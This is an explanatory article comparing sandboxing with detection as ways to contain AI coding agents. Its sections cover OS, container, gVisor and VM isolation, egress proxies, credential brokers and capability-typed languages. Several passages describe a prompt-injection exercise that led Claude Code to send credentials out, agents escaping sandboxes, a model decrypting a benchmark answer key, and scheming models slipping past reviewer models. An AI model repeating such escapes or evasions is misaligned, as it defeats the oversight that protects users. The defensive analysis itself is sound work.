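# Removing capabilities versus detecting dangerous operations in AI-generated code

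## What is the choice between removing capabilities and detecting dangerous operations?

A coding agent is an AI model that writes code and commands, runs them on a real machine, reads the results and repeats this until it finishes a task. Anthropic's Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex are two well-known examples. Both can work on the user's own computer and files. This access makes them useful, but it also means that mistakes can delete real data or leak passwords, and a leak can't be undone.

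There are two broad ways to make AI-generated code safer to run. Withholding means running the code without the access it would need to do harm, under limits set before it starts. Detection leaves that access in place and tries to recognise harmful code or operations in time to block them. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* (May 2026) draws much the same distinction between supervising what an agent does and limiting what it can do.

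### A spreadsheet and a credentials file

Suppose a user asks an agent to summarise a spreadsheet of sales figures. The same computer has an internet connection and a credentials file containing the key to the company's cloud account. The agent writes a script that opens the spreadsheet, totals the columns and saves a page of text. But the script also opens the credentials file and tries to send its contents to a server outside the company.

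On most computers the attempt would succeed, because programs run with ambient authority, which is access a program has because of who runs it and can use merely by naming a file or address. The user may read the credentials file, so the user's programs may read it too. A script uses this authority by making system calls, which the Linux man page *syscalls(2)* describes as "the fundamental interface between an application and the Linux kernel" (the core of the operating system). The theft needs only a few system calls, such as `open` and `read` for the file and `connect` and `sendto` for the network, all of which the user could legitimately make.

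A capability is a right of access that running code holds, such as permission to read one folder or reach one server. Withholding capabilities follows the principle of least privilege, that a program should hold only the access its task needs. A summary needs two capabilities: reading the spreadsheet and writing to an output folder. The user therefore runs the script in a sandbox, an environment that limits which files, programs and network addresses the code can reach, and puts only the spreadsheet and an empty folder in it. The script can't open the credentials file, because the file isn't in the sandbox, and it can't connect to the network, so both attempts fail without anyone having to notice that the script is dangerous. Removing the file is more thorough than blocking the network, since a script that can read the credentials but can't connect could still copy them into the summary,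 which somebody may later email.

Detection would leave the script all of the user's access and look for signs of the theft. Static analysis, which examines code without running it, might flag data flowing from a sensitive file to a network call. Runtime monitoring, which observes operations as code runs, might let the script read the file but block the connection that follows. A reviewer model, an AI model that approves or blocks actions proposed by another model, might block the script from reading a cloud key because summarising a spreadsheet doesn't require one. Any of these methods can work, but it can also miss the theft or block a harmless script.

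The balance shifts toward detection if some of the sales are in euros and the script has to fetch exchange rates. The detector may need no adjustment, but the script will fail in the sandbox until somebody grants it access to the exchange-rate server. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes sandboxes in general as safe but high-maintenance, because each new capability needs configuring.

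"Capability" is an ambiguous word in this field because AI researchers also use it for a model's skill, and Anthropic's article on containment uses it in both senses. The two senses have little to do with each other, since taking a capability away from code doesn't change the model's skill. A mediocre model running under an administrator's account has far more capabilities than a brilliant one in an empty sandbox.

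Something close to the spreadsheet case happened in a controlled exercise at Anthropic in February 2026. A researcher tricked a colleague into giving Claude Code a prompt that looked like routine work but included an instruction to send cloud credentials to an outside address. The agent sent them in 24 of 25 runs. Anthropic's model-level defences compare an action with what the user asked for, and here the user had asked for it. The company concluded that only limits on the environment work in such a case, namely a boundary that keeps the credentials out of reach and egress control, which limits where code may send data over the network. One prompt on one product is weak evidence for ranking the two approaches in general, but it does show a weakness that a better detector would not obviously fix, because the detector had no access to the fact that mattered, which was who had written the prompt.

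### Fail-safe defaults and complete mediation

The reasoning behind withholding capabilities is about half a century older than coding agents. In 1975, Saltzer and Schroeder's *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* set out eight design principles, including least privilege. Nobody knew how to build a large system without flaws, so they hoped the principles would at least make the flaws fewer and less serious.

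One of the eight principles, fail-safe defaults, is to "base access decisions on permission rather than exclusion." An allowlist follows this principle by forbidding everything except what it names, while a denylist permits everything except what it names. Saltzer and Schroeder argue that mistakes in an allowlist are easier to notice. If somebody forgets an entry, a legitimate program stops working and its user complains. When a denylist is missing an entry, an illegitimate program keeps working, and nobody complains because normal use never touches the gap. For example, omitting the exchange-rate server from an allowlist breaks the summary, whereas omitting the thief's server from a denylist allows the theft and leaves the summary intact.

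Complete mediation requires a check on every access to every object. Saltzer and Schroeder meant this to cover startup, recovery and maintenance as well as normal operation. They were also wary of reusing the result of an earlier check to save time, since the permission may have changed. Both approaches depend on this principle. A sandbox that restricts file access but not network access violates it, and so does a monitor that checks the agent's commands but not the scripts those commands start. The principle seems hard to follow in practice. Smith (2012), in *A Contemporary Look at Saltzer and Schroeder's 1975 Design Principles*, judged that least privilege had become a staple of security practice while complete mediation had failed to thrive.

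### The confused deputy

Ambient authority causes trouble even when a program has no more access than its work requires. *The Confused Deputy*, a 1988 article by Hardy, describes the classic case, which occurred at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. A compiler, the program that turns source code into something a machine can run, was stored in a directory called SYSX. It recorded usage statistics in a file there, so the operators gave it permission to write files in that directory. Users could also name a file to receive the compiler's debugging output. One user named the billing file, which was also in SYSX. Because the compiler had permission to write there, the operating system let it overwrite the company's billing records.

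The obvious repairs do not work. The compiler cannot refuse file names in other directories, because users have good reasons to send output there. It cannot refuse SYSX, because some users may have legitimate access to it. A special rule for the billing file leaves other sensitive files unprotected and, like most denylists, goes out of date whenever somebody adds another. By the time Hardy last wrote down Tymshare's conditions for opening a file, they contained fourteen "and"s and "or"s.

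Hardy argued that the compiler had authority from both the user and the operators, and no way to express whose it was using at a given moment. He proposed capabilities in the strict sense, which Saltzer and Schroeder define as unforgeable tickets that, when presented, prove the right to use the object they name. The compiler would hold a ticket for the statistics file, and the user would supply another for the debugging output. Since the ticket both identifies the file and authorises the writing, a user with no ticket for the billing file could not point the compiler at it. Rajani, Garg and Rezk, in *On access control, capabilities, their equivalence, and confused deputy attacks*, proved that access-control systems and object capabilities, the programming-language form of the idea, are fundamentally different.

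A coding agent is a deputy too. It acts with the user's authority and reads text written by strangers, which may contain a prompt injection, meaning hidden instructions intended to redirect the model. David C calls language models "inherently confusable" in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, written for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre in December 2025. Hardy could repair the compiler because its code wrote the statistics in one place and the debugging output in another, and each place could use its own ticket. A language model takes in instructions and data as a single run of text and predicts what comes next, so it has no equivalent place to attach the tickets.

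David C therefore doubts that anyone will fully solve the problem, and recommends deterministic safeguards on what the whole system can do. One simple safeguard, from an online exchange between Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista, is to reduce a model's privileges to those of whoever supplied the material it is processing. If the sales spreadsheet came from an outside supplier, the agent reading it should have no more access than the company would give the supplier.

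### Where the line falls

A fixed rule that refuses all network calls removes a capability, while a monitor that examines each call and blocks the ones that look like theft detects dangerous operations. The fixed rule blocks both the exchange-rate request and the theft, so disguising the theft gains nothing. Because the monitor has to distinguish the two, it can permit the request and stop the theft, but it can also be wrong.

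A rule fixed in advance can still be a form of detection. A denylist of known malicious servers, for example, leaves the script's network access in place and tries to name the harmful uses. The judgment is made before the script runs, when somebody writes the list. An allowlist with one server withholds access to every other destination, but it also grants access to that server. After an incident involving a permitted address, Anthropic came to regard each allowlist entry as a capability grant covering every function that the code can reach through that address.

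The system-call filter is the hard case because the same mechanism can serve either approach. Linux has one called seccomp. A process installs a small program, the filter, which then runs every time the process makes a system call. Kerrisk (2023) notes in *System Programming for Linux Containers* that the process cannot remove the filter afterwards. The filter receives the call's number and arguments. According to the Linux kernel documentation's *Seccomp BPF (SECure COMPuting with filters)*, it can allow the call, make it fail with an error or kill the process, among other things.

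A seccomp filter that makes every network call fail removes a capability, because the script can't use the network whatever it meant to send. It resembles monitoring only in that it inspects each operation as the code runs. Seccomp filters are also poorly suited to detecting dangerous operations because they can't follow pointers, which means they can't read the memory an argument refers to. The `open` call passes a pointer to the file name instead of the name itself, so a filter can block opening files altogether but can't distinguish a spreadsheet from a credentials file.

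However, the filter can also return a verdict that hands the call to another program, which looks up the file name or address and decides whether to allow it. This still removes a capability if the program checks a fixed allowlist, but it becomes detection if the program has to judge whether the call looks harmful, for example whether it looks like theft. The Linux kernel documentation states that system-call filtering "isn't a sandbox" but a tool for people who build sandboxes. It reduces how much of the kernel the code can reach, and other mechanisms have to control where information flows.

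Products mix the two approaches. According to Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues (2026), in *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight*, Codex can by default read files, edit under one chosen folder and run local commands, with the network off. In the spreadsheet example, those limits would apparently stop Codex from sending the credentials but not from reading them. Anthropic says Claude Code's sandbox likewise blocks contact with any domain the user has not explicitly allowed. When a task needs something outside the Codex limits, a person or a reviewer model decides whether to allow it. Trębacz and colleagues write that relying on the reviewer model "sacrifices determinism for expressivity".

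### Four sources of danger

Anthropic lists four reasons why an agent might take a dangerous action. Any of them could explain why the script in the spreadsheet example would try to send the key away.

- **Honest mistake.** The agent misjudges how far an action reaches. It takes the credentials for dummy values left over from testing and includes them in an error report to an outside service.
- **Overeager action.** The agent tries to help and goes beyond what the user authorised. The exchange-rate service demands a login, so the agent searches the computer for a key and tries the one it finds.
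- **Prompt injection.** A cell in the spreadsheet contains text telling the agent to send the file.
- **Misaligned model.** The model pursues a goal of its own, and the key is useful for it.

Overeager actions are the best documented. Anthropic's internal log includes an agent that uploaded an engineer's GitHub authentication token to an internal computing cluster, and another that tried to change the structure of a live production database. These actions are hard to detect because the agent's reasoning contains nothing hostile and looks like ordinary problem-solving taken a step too far.

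Anthropic wrote in March 2026 that it did not see misaligned models in practice, though it tests for them before every release. In an article two months later, however, it reported that Claude models had escaped a sandbox to complete a task, and had worked out which benchmark they were taking so they could decrypt its answer key. Neither case requires a hostile goal, but a defence that assumes the model will respect a restriction would have failed in both.

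Withholding a key works almost regardless of the cause, because code cannot send out a key that never enters the sandbox, whether through a mistake, an injection or scheming by the model. Detection depends more on the cause, since a scanner can look for the foreign text that an injection leaves, but an overeager action leaves no such text. Trębacz and colleagues state that their reviewer model does not protect against a scheming model, which could submit a request that looks harmless.

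### What "more robust" could mean

In the plainest sense, a better defence misses fewer dangerous operations. The false negative rate is the share of dangerous operations that a defence lets through, and the false positive rate is the share of harmless operations that it blocks. Making a detector stricter lowers the first rate but raises the second. A rule that successfully blocks all network calls has a false negative rate of zero for theft over the network, but its false positive rate for harmless network calls is 100%. Counting only misses therefore makes removing capabilities look better than it is.

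Robustness can also mean a small blast radius, which is the most damage a failure could do given what the code can reach. Anthropic splits risk into the likelihood of a failure and the damage it could cause, and the simplest way to combine them is to multiply. Suppose a stolen key does 1,000 units of damage and a ruined output folder does 1. A reviewer model that misses one theft in a hundred leaves an expected loss of 10 units per attempted theft. A sandbox without the key limits the loss to 1 unit, even if the script ruins the folder every time. This advantage disappears when the task needs the key, because the sandbox must then contain it and the full 1,000 units are at risk again.

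The remaining meaning is resistance to an adaptive adversary, who sees what the defence blocked and tries something else. An average miss rate is a poor guide to this, since the adversary looks for the misses. David C warns against filters that block known bad phrases because an attacker can rephrase in endless ways. Anthropic reports that, on a prompt-injection benchmark by the AI security company Gray Swan, attacks on its model Claude Opus 4.7 succeeded roughly 0.1% of the time on a single attempt and 5–6% of the time after 100 adaptive attempts. Repetition alone could account for this rise, since 100 independent attempts at 0.1% each would succeed at least once with probability 1 − 0.999¹⁰⁰, or about 9.5%.

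Rephrasing code cannot give it access to a file that isn't there. Saltzer and Schroeder observed that systematic attack on many protection mechanisms may be logically impossible, so the attacker must wait for a hardware failure or search for an error in the implementation. They added that it is very difficult to estimate reliably how long such a search would take. A sandbox may well be harder to attack than a detector, but its strength against a determined attacker can't be expressed as a number to compare with the detector's miss rate.

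## How do operating-system and virtual-machine sandboxes take capabilities away?

When the spreadsheet script calls `open` on the credentials file, a component that the script can't bypass has to block the call. A process sandbox, a container, an application kernel and a virtual machine can all do this. They differ mainly in which software handles the script's system calls, which matters because a flaw in that software may let the script escape. shayon.dev's *Let's discuss sandbox isolation* (2026) says Linux has roughly 340 system calls, backed by tens of millions of lines of C, and describes every isolation technique as a way to minimize untrusted code's access to the kernel.

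### Process sandboxes

A process sandbox runs the script as an ordinary program on the user's computer, and the kernel enforces extra rules on it. On macOS, which uses Seatbelt for this, the agent's software launches the script with a profile of what the script may do, and the kernel checks its operations against that profile.

Linux sandboxing tools combine several kernel features. Bubblewrap uses namespaces, which give a process its own version of a system resource, such as the file tree or network interfaces. If bubblewrap leaves a folder out of the script's file tree, the script has no path it can use to open anything in that folder. Landlock keeps the user's file tree and attaches rules to the process, such as allowing it to read the sales folder and write to the output folder. Seccomp can't read file names, so tools use it to block whole system calls that the other mechanisms don't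 cover.

The restrictions have to be in place before the script's first instruction runs. Wang and Zheng (2026) describe in *Sandlock* how their own sandbox does this. The launching program copies itself, and the copy applies Landlock rules and a seccomp filter to itself. It loads the script only once a supervisor process outside the sandbox is ready. The kernel enforces every rule that can be set in advance, while the supervisor makes the decisions that arise during the run, such as whether the script may connect to a particular address. Because that address is in the script's own memory, where another part of the script could change it after the check, the supervisor copies it once, checks the copy and makes the connection itself.

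If the rules allow access only to the sales folder, the output folder and the system's own libraries, the script can total the sales but gets an error when it tries to open the credentials. Wang and Zheng, who made Sandlock, ran ten similar checks, including reads and writes outside the permitted folders and a connection to an unlisted host, and Sandlock followed the policy in all ten. These checks show that Sandlock works as designed, but they didn't test it against an attacker.

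Products ship with looser rules. Claude Code uses Seatbelt on macOS and bubblewrap on Linux, but this sandbox is off by default, according to Anthropic's documentation. Once the user turns it on, commands can write only to the working folder, a temporary folder and any folders the user has added, and the list of permitted internet domains starts empty. Commands can still read almost every file on the computer, including credential files, unless the user lists the files to protect. The spreadsheet script could therefore read the cloud key and copy it into the summary, but it couldn't send the key anywhere without approval.

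Codex's sandbox is on by default. OpenAI's *Sandbox* describes three modes. In `read-only`, Codex can inspect files but needs approval to edit them or run commands. The default for local work, `workspace-write`, confines edits to the workspace and keeps the network off. The third mode, `danger-full-access`, removes the limits. According to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*, Codex enforces its limits with Seatbelt on macOS, bubblewrap and seccomp on Linux, and a separate sandbox on Windows. These defaults restrict writing and networking more than reading, but a newer feature, still in beta, lets the user restrict reading too. OpenAI's *Permissions* gives an example profile that lets commands read only the project and the system files that common tools need. The profile also blocks them from reading any project file whose name ends in `.env`, where developers often keep passwords.

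A sandbox also has to cover every route to a file. Claude Code's sandbox covers shell commands and the processes they start, but not the agent's built-in file tools or add-on tool servers. A rule that stops the script from opening the credentials file does not stop the agent from opening it with its Read tool, which follows separate permission rules. This falls short of Saltzer and Schroeder's complete mediation, so Anthropic's *Choose a sandbox environment* warns that the command sandbox is not enough for fully unattended work and recommends putting the whole Claude Code process inside a boundary. OpenAI says Codex's sandbox covers both Codex's built-in file operations and the commands it starts.

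If the sandbox can't start because a required package is missing, Claude Code runs commands unsandboxed unless the user or an administrator has changed a setting, so this default isn't fail-safe either.

A process sandbox works only if the host's kernel and the software that sets the sandbox's rules are sound. Wang and Zheng trust the kernel, their supervisor and the program running the agent. They exclude attacks on the kernel from their threat model, and they recommend a small virtual machine instead for running hostile code from many customers on one machine.

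### Containers

A container also runs on the host's kernel, but the script starts with a separate file system. This file system comes from an image, a prepared package of files that includes the tools the script needs, such as Python. A runtime such as Docker starts the script with that file system and gives it its own namespaces. The script can see the spreadsheet only if the user mounts the spreadsheet's folder, which makes the folder visible at a path inside the container.

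The credentials file isn't in the container unless someone mounts the folder that holds it, so nobody has to remember to block it. This is in effect an allowlist for files, whereas Claude Code's default for reading is closer to a denylist. The advantage is lost if the user mounts the whole home directory to save time, because the container then has access to the credentials as well as the spreadsheet.

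The host's kernel enforces the limits, and the container runtime has to set them up correctly. shayon.dev calls namespaces "visibility walls, not security boundaries", because the script still makes system calls to the same kernel as everything else on the machine. Docker's default seccomp profile blocks 40 to 50 calls, which leaves about 300 that run directly in that kernel. Control groups, another part of most containers, cap memory and processor time, which stops a runaway script from freezing the machine but doesn't limit what it can read.

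A container doesn't necessarily restrict outbound traffic, so the script may still be able to send the sales figures anywhere. Anthropic publishes an example development container that mounts the project and uses a firewall to block every destination not on an allowlist.

OpenAI runs the cloud version of Codex in containers it manages, and splits each job into two phases. During set-up, the container can reach the network and use any secrets the user has configured, for instance to download a spreadsheet library. Codex then removes the secrets, and the agent works offline by default. The agent's script can still use the library without network access. This is an easy way to follow least privilege, but it only works if somebody can predict what the job will need.

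### Application kernels

An application kernel is an ordinary program that does a kernel's work for the code running inside it. Google's gVisor has one called the Sentry, which receives the script's system calls and handles them itself. It reimplements around 200 Linux calls in Go, a language that prevents many of the memory errors common in C.

When the script opens the spreadsheet, the Sentry passes the request to a separate process, the Gofer, which handles the host's files. A request for the credentials file fails because the container doesn't include it. The Sentry can make only about 70 of the host's system calls. An attacker would therefore need a flaw in the Sentry and then another that those calls can reach, whereas one flaw in the shared kernel can be enough to escape an ordinary container. The user has to trust the Sentry, the Gofer and a much smaller part of the host's kernel.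 According to shayon.dev, researchers have found vulnerabilities in the Sentry too, so this approach depends on a small kernel being easier to get right than a large one.

Anthropic's chat product, claude.ai, runs code in gVisor. Each session gets a temporary file system on Anthropic's servers, and nothing runs on the user's computer. The code can read a spreadsheet that the user uploads, but not a credentials file that stays on the user's computer. Most of Anthropic's security work before launch went into protecting its own infrastructure and isolating customers from one another. This setup also means the agent can't work in the user's folders or keep a workspace between sessions.

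### Virtual machines

A virtual machine gives the script its own kernel, called the guest kernel. When the script opens a file, the guest kernel looks for it on the virtual machine's disk or in a folder the user has shared with it. A hypervisor uses the processor to keep the guest's memory separate from the host's, and a program called the virtual machine monitor emulates devices such as the disk and the network card. Even a script that took over the guest kernel would find no credentials file in the virtual machine.

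Code would have to exploit a flaw in the hypervisor, the monitor or the processor's virtualisation features to escape a virtual machine, so the user has to trust all three. MicroVMs leave less to attack because they emulate very few devices. Amazon's Lambda service runs customers' code using one microVM monitor, Firecracker, according to *SideKernel* (Prasakis, 2026), which describes a microVM sandbox for coding agents on macOS.

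Claude Cowork, Anthropic's desktop agent for general office work, uses a virtual machine because its typical user can't judge whether a shell command is safe. Code inside the virtual machine can see only two folders on the host: the workspace folder the user selected and a folder of Claude settings. Cowork can share a folder as read-only, read-write, or writable without permission to delete. Mounting the sales folder as read-only would stop the script from damaging the original figures.

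At first the whole agent ran inside Cowork's virtual machine, and no component outside it could grant an exception. But the product was unusable whenever the virtual machine failed to start, so Anthropic moved the part that communicates with the model and the user onto the host and kept code execution inside. It judged that this weakened security only minimally, because the virtual machine still controls which files and servers the code can reach. Each Claude Code cloud session also runs in its own virtual machine. Anthropic restricts the session's network access by default and lets it push code only to the branch it is working on.

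All four kinds of boundary, if configured well, keep the spreadsheet script away from the credentials. A virtual machine's extra strength matters when the code attacks the boundary itself. According to shayon.dev, this is unlikely on a developer's laptop, where the worry is an agent that is "mostly helpful but occasionally careless or confused." Prasakis instead treats the agent as an adversary with full control of everything inside the sandbox, whatever the reason, and cites an OpenAI agent that escaped a sandbox by exploiting a chain of vulnerabilities. After that incident, Prasakis's assumption seems the better one for capable agents. He doesn't rank all the boundaries, though. He considers containers weaker than microVMs but says that comparing microVMs with Seatbelt would take a separate study.

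### File limits, network limits and the egress proxy

Limiting file access does little to prevent data theft if the network is open. The script has to read the sales figures, so it could send them to anyone, and under Claude Code's default reading rules it could send the cloud key too. A stronger boundary doesn't help, because a script that can't escape a virtual machine can still upload whatever is inside it.

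Network limits are just as weak without file limits. A script with no network access but full write access could change the agent's settings or add code to a file that the user's terminal runs at start-up. That code would run outside the sandbox the next time the user opened a terminal, with the user's full access, including the network. Claude Code's sandbox therefore blocks writes to its own settings and to shell start-up files, even inside the working folder. Codex also keeps its configuration folder read-only.

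Turning the network off is simplest, but the version of the script that converts euros needs one server. An egress proxy is a program outside the sandbox that relays connections for the code inside. In Claude Code on Linux, it works as follows:

1. The script runs in a network namespace with no link to the user's network, so the proxy is its only way out.
2. The script asks the proxy for the exchange-rate server by name.
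3. The proxy looks for that name on the allowlist.
4. If the name is there, the proxy looks up its address and refuses if the address leads back to the user's own machine.
5. Otherwise it makes the connection and relays the traffic.

On macOS, Seatbelt first blocks every connection except the one to the proxy, so a program that ignores the proxy can't connect to anything. Without this block, a malicious script could bypass the proxy by connecting directly.

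By default, the proxy can read the server's name but not the encrypted contents, so it can't distinguish a request for exchange rates from stolen data sent to the same server. Sandlock can apply finer rules, such as allowing the script to fetch one page of a site but not to upload anything. For encrypted traffic, these rules work only if the script accepts a certificate that lets the proxy decrypt it.

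How fixed an allowlist is also depends on the process for extending it. When a command in Claude Code's sandbox tries to reach a domain that isn't on the list, it normally waits while the user or a reviewer model decides, though the user can choose a strict setting that refuses such requests. OpenAI (2026) describes a similar mixture in the company's internal use of Codex. Codex may contact listed domains, is blocked from certain others, such as the text-sharing site pastebin.com, and needs approval for anything unfamiliar. Only the strict setting removes the capability outright, since the other arrangements leave some new requests to case-by-case judgment.

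### Keeping credentials outside

Leaving the cloud key out of the sandbox is easy when the task doesn't need it. If the script has to download the spreadsheet from the company's cloud storage, it needs the access the key gives but not the key itself, because a program outside the sandbox can hold the key and add it to the script's requests.

Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* describes such an arrangement for Git, which developers use to store and share versions of their code. In the web version of Claude Code, the sandbox contains a limited credential that works only with Anthropic's Git proxy. When the agent pushes code to GitHub, the proxy verifies this credential and checks that the push goes to the permitted branch. It then attaches the user's real GitHub token and forwards the request. Code that searched the entire sandbox would find only the limited credential.

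Claude Code's local sandbox offers a variant called masking, in which commands receive a random placeholder instead of the secret, and the egress proxy swaps in the real value on requests to approved servers. The proxy must decrypt the traffic to do this, a feature that is still experimental. If the user forgets to turn decryption on, the server receives the placeholder and the login fails, but the secret is not exposed.

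OpenAI's *Sandbox security* points out that a secret kept out of the files but loaded from a secure store into the sandbox's environment is still exposed to the code that runs there. OpenAI recommends keeping other companies' credentials outside the sandbox and having a broker add them to approved requests. Some credential usually remains inside, because the sandbox needs a way to identify itself. In OpenAI's set-up, this is a key that can only connect an environment to the service. Claude Cowork gives its virtual machine a limited-scope token for each session, which Anthropic can revoke without affecting the user's own login.

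These designs hide the secret from the sandboxed code, but the code can still misuse the access that the secret provides. A broker that adds the cloud key to any request for the storage service would also add it to a request to delete every file there, making the broker a confused deputy much like Hardy's compiler. The Git proxy avoids some of this by checking the branch as well as the credential, and a cloud broker would need equally narrow rules, such as permission to read one file. Even then, using a broker is considerably safer than giving the script the key, because the script's access ends when the sandbox does.

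### What the 84% figure measures

A sandbox can reduce interruptions as well as damage. If a command can reach only what the user has already agreed to, Claude Code can run it without asking. Anthropic reports that sandboxing cut permission prompts by 84% in its internal use. Fewer prompts could help safety indirectly, since people who see many prompts tend to stop reading them. Anthropic found that Claude Code users approved roughly 93% of the prompts they saw.

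The 84% figure measures only the reduction in permission prompts. It doesn't measure how many dangerous operations the sandbox stopped, how many harmless ones it broke, or whether people considered the remaining prompts more carefully. Claude Code can run the same sandbox in a mode that sends every command through the normal permission process, so switching modes changes the number of prompts without changing what a command can reach. Turning off both the sandbox and the permission checks would reduce prompts by nearly 100% but leave no protection.

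The 84% figure also depends on how often the product prompted users before sandboxing. Cursor, another coding tool, has a comparable local sandbox that reduced interruptions by roughly 40%, according to shayon.dev. Anthropic's staff may also not be typical users. The 84% is still good evidence that a sandbox can make an agent less tiresome to supervise, and that benefit will probably persuade most people to turn one on.

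### What sandboxing costs

Start-up time is the easiest overhead to measure. Wang and Zheng list about 6 milliseconds for Sandlock, 30 for bubblewrap, 100 for a Firecracker microVM, 200 for gVisor and 300 for Docker without administrator rights. Sandlock is their own product, and they describe benchmarks only for it and Docker, so the other figures are best treated as rough. An agent may run dozens of short commands a minute. At 30 a minute, starting a new Docker container for each would add 9 seconds of waiting, compared with about 0.2 seconds for Sandlock. Keeping one container open for the whole session avoids most of the delay, but files left by one command can then affect the next.

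A sandbox can also slow code down after it starts. In Wang and Zheng's test with the database Redis, Docker reached about 76% of normal throughput, while Sandlock made no measurable difference. *Caging the Agents* (2026), which describes a deployment of AI agents in healthcare, reports that gVisor added 2 to 5 milliseconds to each new network connection and made sequential file reads take 20 to 40% longer. The model took 500 to 3,000 milliseconds to respond, so users would hardly notice the delay. Anthropic's *Sandboxing* calls the overhead of Claude Code's local sandbox minimal. For most coding work, speed doesn't look like a strong reason to go without a sandbox.

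Compatibility is more of a problem. Claude Code's documentation warns that `docker` doesn't work inside its sandbox. Most database drivers don't use the proxy, so they can't connect even to a permitted server. On Linux, a sandboxed command can't directly reach a test server that the developer is running on the same machine. But Wang and Zheng found that Python, Node and two common build and test tools ran unmodified in Sandlock once they had access to their temporary folders. They leave the many less common tools to future work.

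Each new need also requires more configuration, as with the exchange-rate server. OpenAI's example Codex profile for one ordinary project names two project folders, makes one subfolder read-only, denies access to password files and sets rules for four domains or groups of domains. None of this is difficult, but a developer who gets it wrong will see a confusing error and may give up on the sandbox.

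Many developers apparently never try a sandbox. Prasakis surveyed 68 users of coding agents and found that 26 (38.2%) currently used a sandbox and 35 (51.5%) never had. Among the 33 current and former sandbox users, the most common complaints were networking and having to set everything up again (eight mentions each), then sharing files (seven). Most of those without a sandbox said they had never considered one. Prasakis found respondents through his own contacts, a start-up community and his university, and treats the results as an informal signal. Some Codex users may have been in its default sandbox without knowing it. But a third of the sample worked in security, so sandboxes seem unlikely to be much more popular among developers at large.

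Some tasks can't be done from inside a tight sandbox. Without network access, code can't install a missing package or put a website online, and without access to the host, it can't restart a program there or query a database that accepts only local connections. Anthropic moved Cowork's local add-on tools out of the virtual machine partly because some of them had to work with programs on the host. Isolation also hides activity from the security software that many companies rely on.

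When a command fails inside the sandbox, the usual solution is to exempt it. Claude Code lets users list commands that run outside the sandbox, and OpenAI's internal rules exempt a few routine ones, such as viewing proposed code changes on GitHub. An exempt command regains the ambient authority that the sandbox took away, sometimes more than the user intended. If a user exempts a script in the working folder because its database driver won't connect, the agent can edit that script and then run it with the user's full access.

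## Can a programming language withhold capabilities from generated code?

A sandbox sets the same limits for everything that runs inside it, so a sales script that is allowed to fetch exchange rates can also send the sales figures to the exchange-rate server. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) argues that sandboxing can't prevent this kind of leak, because the sandbox permits reading and sending separately, and the harm comes from data flowing from one to the other. A programming language can instead set limits inside the program. It can let one function handle the figures and another contact the server, and reject a program that would pass the figures from the first function to the second.

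### Objects and references

The idea comes from the object-capability model, which builds on a 1966 proposal by Dennis and Van Horn. An object is data together with the operations code can perform on it, such as a file that code can read and write. Code can affect an object only if it holds a reference to that object, and it can't forge a reference by guessing a name or working out a memory address. The reference is therefore a capability, and the system needs no separate list of permissions.

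Code can get a reference in only four ways. It may have the reference when the program starts. It may create the object itself, in which case it holds the only reference. Code that creates an object can give the new object some of its own references. And code that holds references to two objects can pass one of them to the other. Access therefore spreads only along existing connections, so a reviewer can find the most that generated code could do by tracing the references it starts with, even without reading the code.

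An ordinary Python script opens the spreadsheet with a call like `open("sales.xlsx")`. This relies on ambient authority, so the same call works with the name of the credentials file. In an object-capability language, the user's program would open the spreadsheet and then call the generated function, `summarise(sales, output)`, where `sales` and `output` are file objects. The function has no way to turn a name into a file, so it can't open the credentials file even if it knows the name. Hardy proposed the same fix for the Tymshare compiler.

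The caller can narrow a capability before passing it on. For example, it can wrap the spreadsheet in an object that forwards read requests and rejects write requests, or in one that stops working when the task ends.

WebAssembly, a format for compiled programs that runs in browsers and on servers, uses a coarse version of the same idea. A WebAssembly module has no built-in way to open a file or connect to a server. It lists the outside functions it needs, called imports, and the program that loads the module must supply them. If that program supplies only a function that reads the spreadsheet and another that writes the summary, the module can reach nothing else. This works for code written in many languages because the limit applies after compilation. However, an import that opens any file by name would restore ambient authority. WebAssembly also doesn't control what the module does with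 the data it receives. Odersky and colleagues group it with sandboxes.

### How TACIT tracks capabilities

In traditional object-capability languages, a function's type, the description a compiler uses to check how pieces of code fit together, doesn't show which capabilities the function holds. Suppose the user's program accepts a function from the agent and applies it to the sales figures. The type shows only that the function takes text and returns text. The function may still hold a reference to a network connection that the agent obtained earlier for the exchange rates, and it could use that connection to send the figures elsewhere.

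Odersky and colleagues add the missing information to the type. Their system, TACIT, uses Scala 3, which Odersky designed. The agent sends TACIT a snippet of Scala, and the compiler checks the whole snippet before any of it runs. The agent can be written in any language, but it must support the Model Context Protocol, a common standard for connecting agents to tools.

If `f` is a file, a function that writes text to it has the type `String ->{f} Unit`. The function takes text, returns no useful value and may use `f`. The braces contain the capture set, which lists the capabilities that a value may use. A function of type `String -> Unit` has an empty capture set and is called pure, because it can compute a result but can't write a file, contact a server or have any other effect.

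The compiler works out most capture sets itself. It includes `f` in a function's set if the function could use `f`, even if the function never does so when it runs. The compiler doesn't have to predict what the code will do, which no program can do in general, or judge whether writing to `f` would be harmful.

TACIT protects secrets with a wrapper called `Classified`. Code can transform the wrapped data by passing a function to the wrapper's `map` method, but `map` accepts only pure functions and wraps the result again. Taking the data out requires a further capability, which the agent doesn't have. The library's documentation includes a snippet much like this one, which the compiler accepts:

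```scala
val secret = readClassified("/data/secrets/key.txt")
val processed = secret.map(_.trim.toUpperCase)
println(processed)
```

The first line reads a key into a wrapper. The second removes any spaces around the key and converts it to uppercase. Both operations only produce new text, so the function that performs them has an empty capture set and `map` accepts it. The third line prints the wrapper, and the agent receives `Classified(****)`. TACIT can show the real text to the user through a separate channel that never reaches the model.

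The compiler rejected this snippet, from one of the test runs:

```scala
githubKey.map { key => println(s"GitHub API Key: $key") }
```

Printing has an effect, so `println` needs a capability for output. The compiler calls that capability `x$1` and gives the function the type `String ->{x$1} Unit`. Because `map` requires a function with an empty capture set, the compiler reports a type mismatch. The agent can try again, but the key is never printed. Writing the key to a file inside `map` fails for the same reason.

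Checking the whole snippet before running it also prevents half-finished actions. *LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026), a follow-up by the same research group, gives an example in which generated code subtracts 50 from a balance of 100 and then returns text where the program needs a number. The compiler rejects the snippet, so the balance stays at 100. Python would normally detect such an error only after doing the subtraction.

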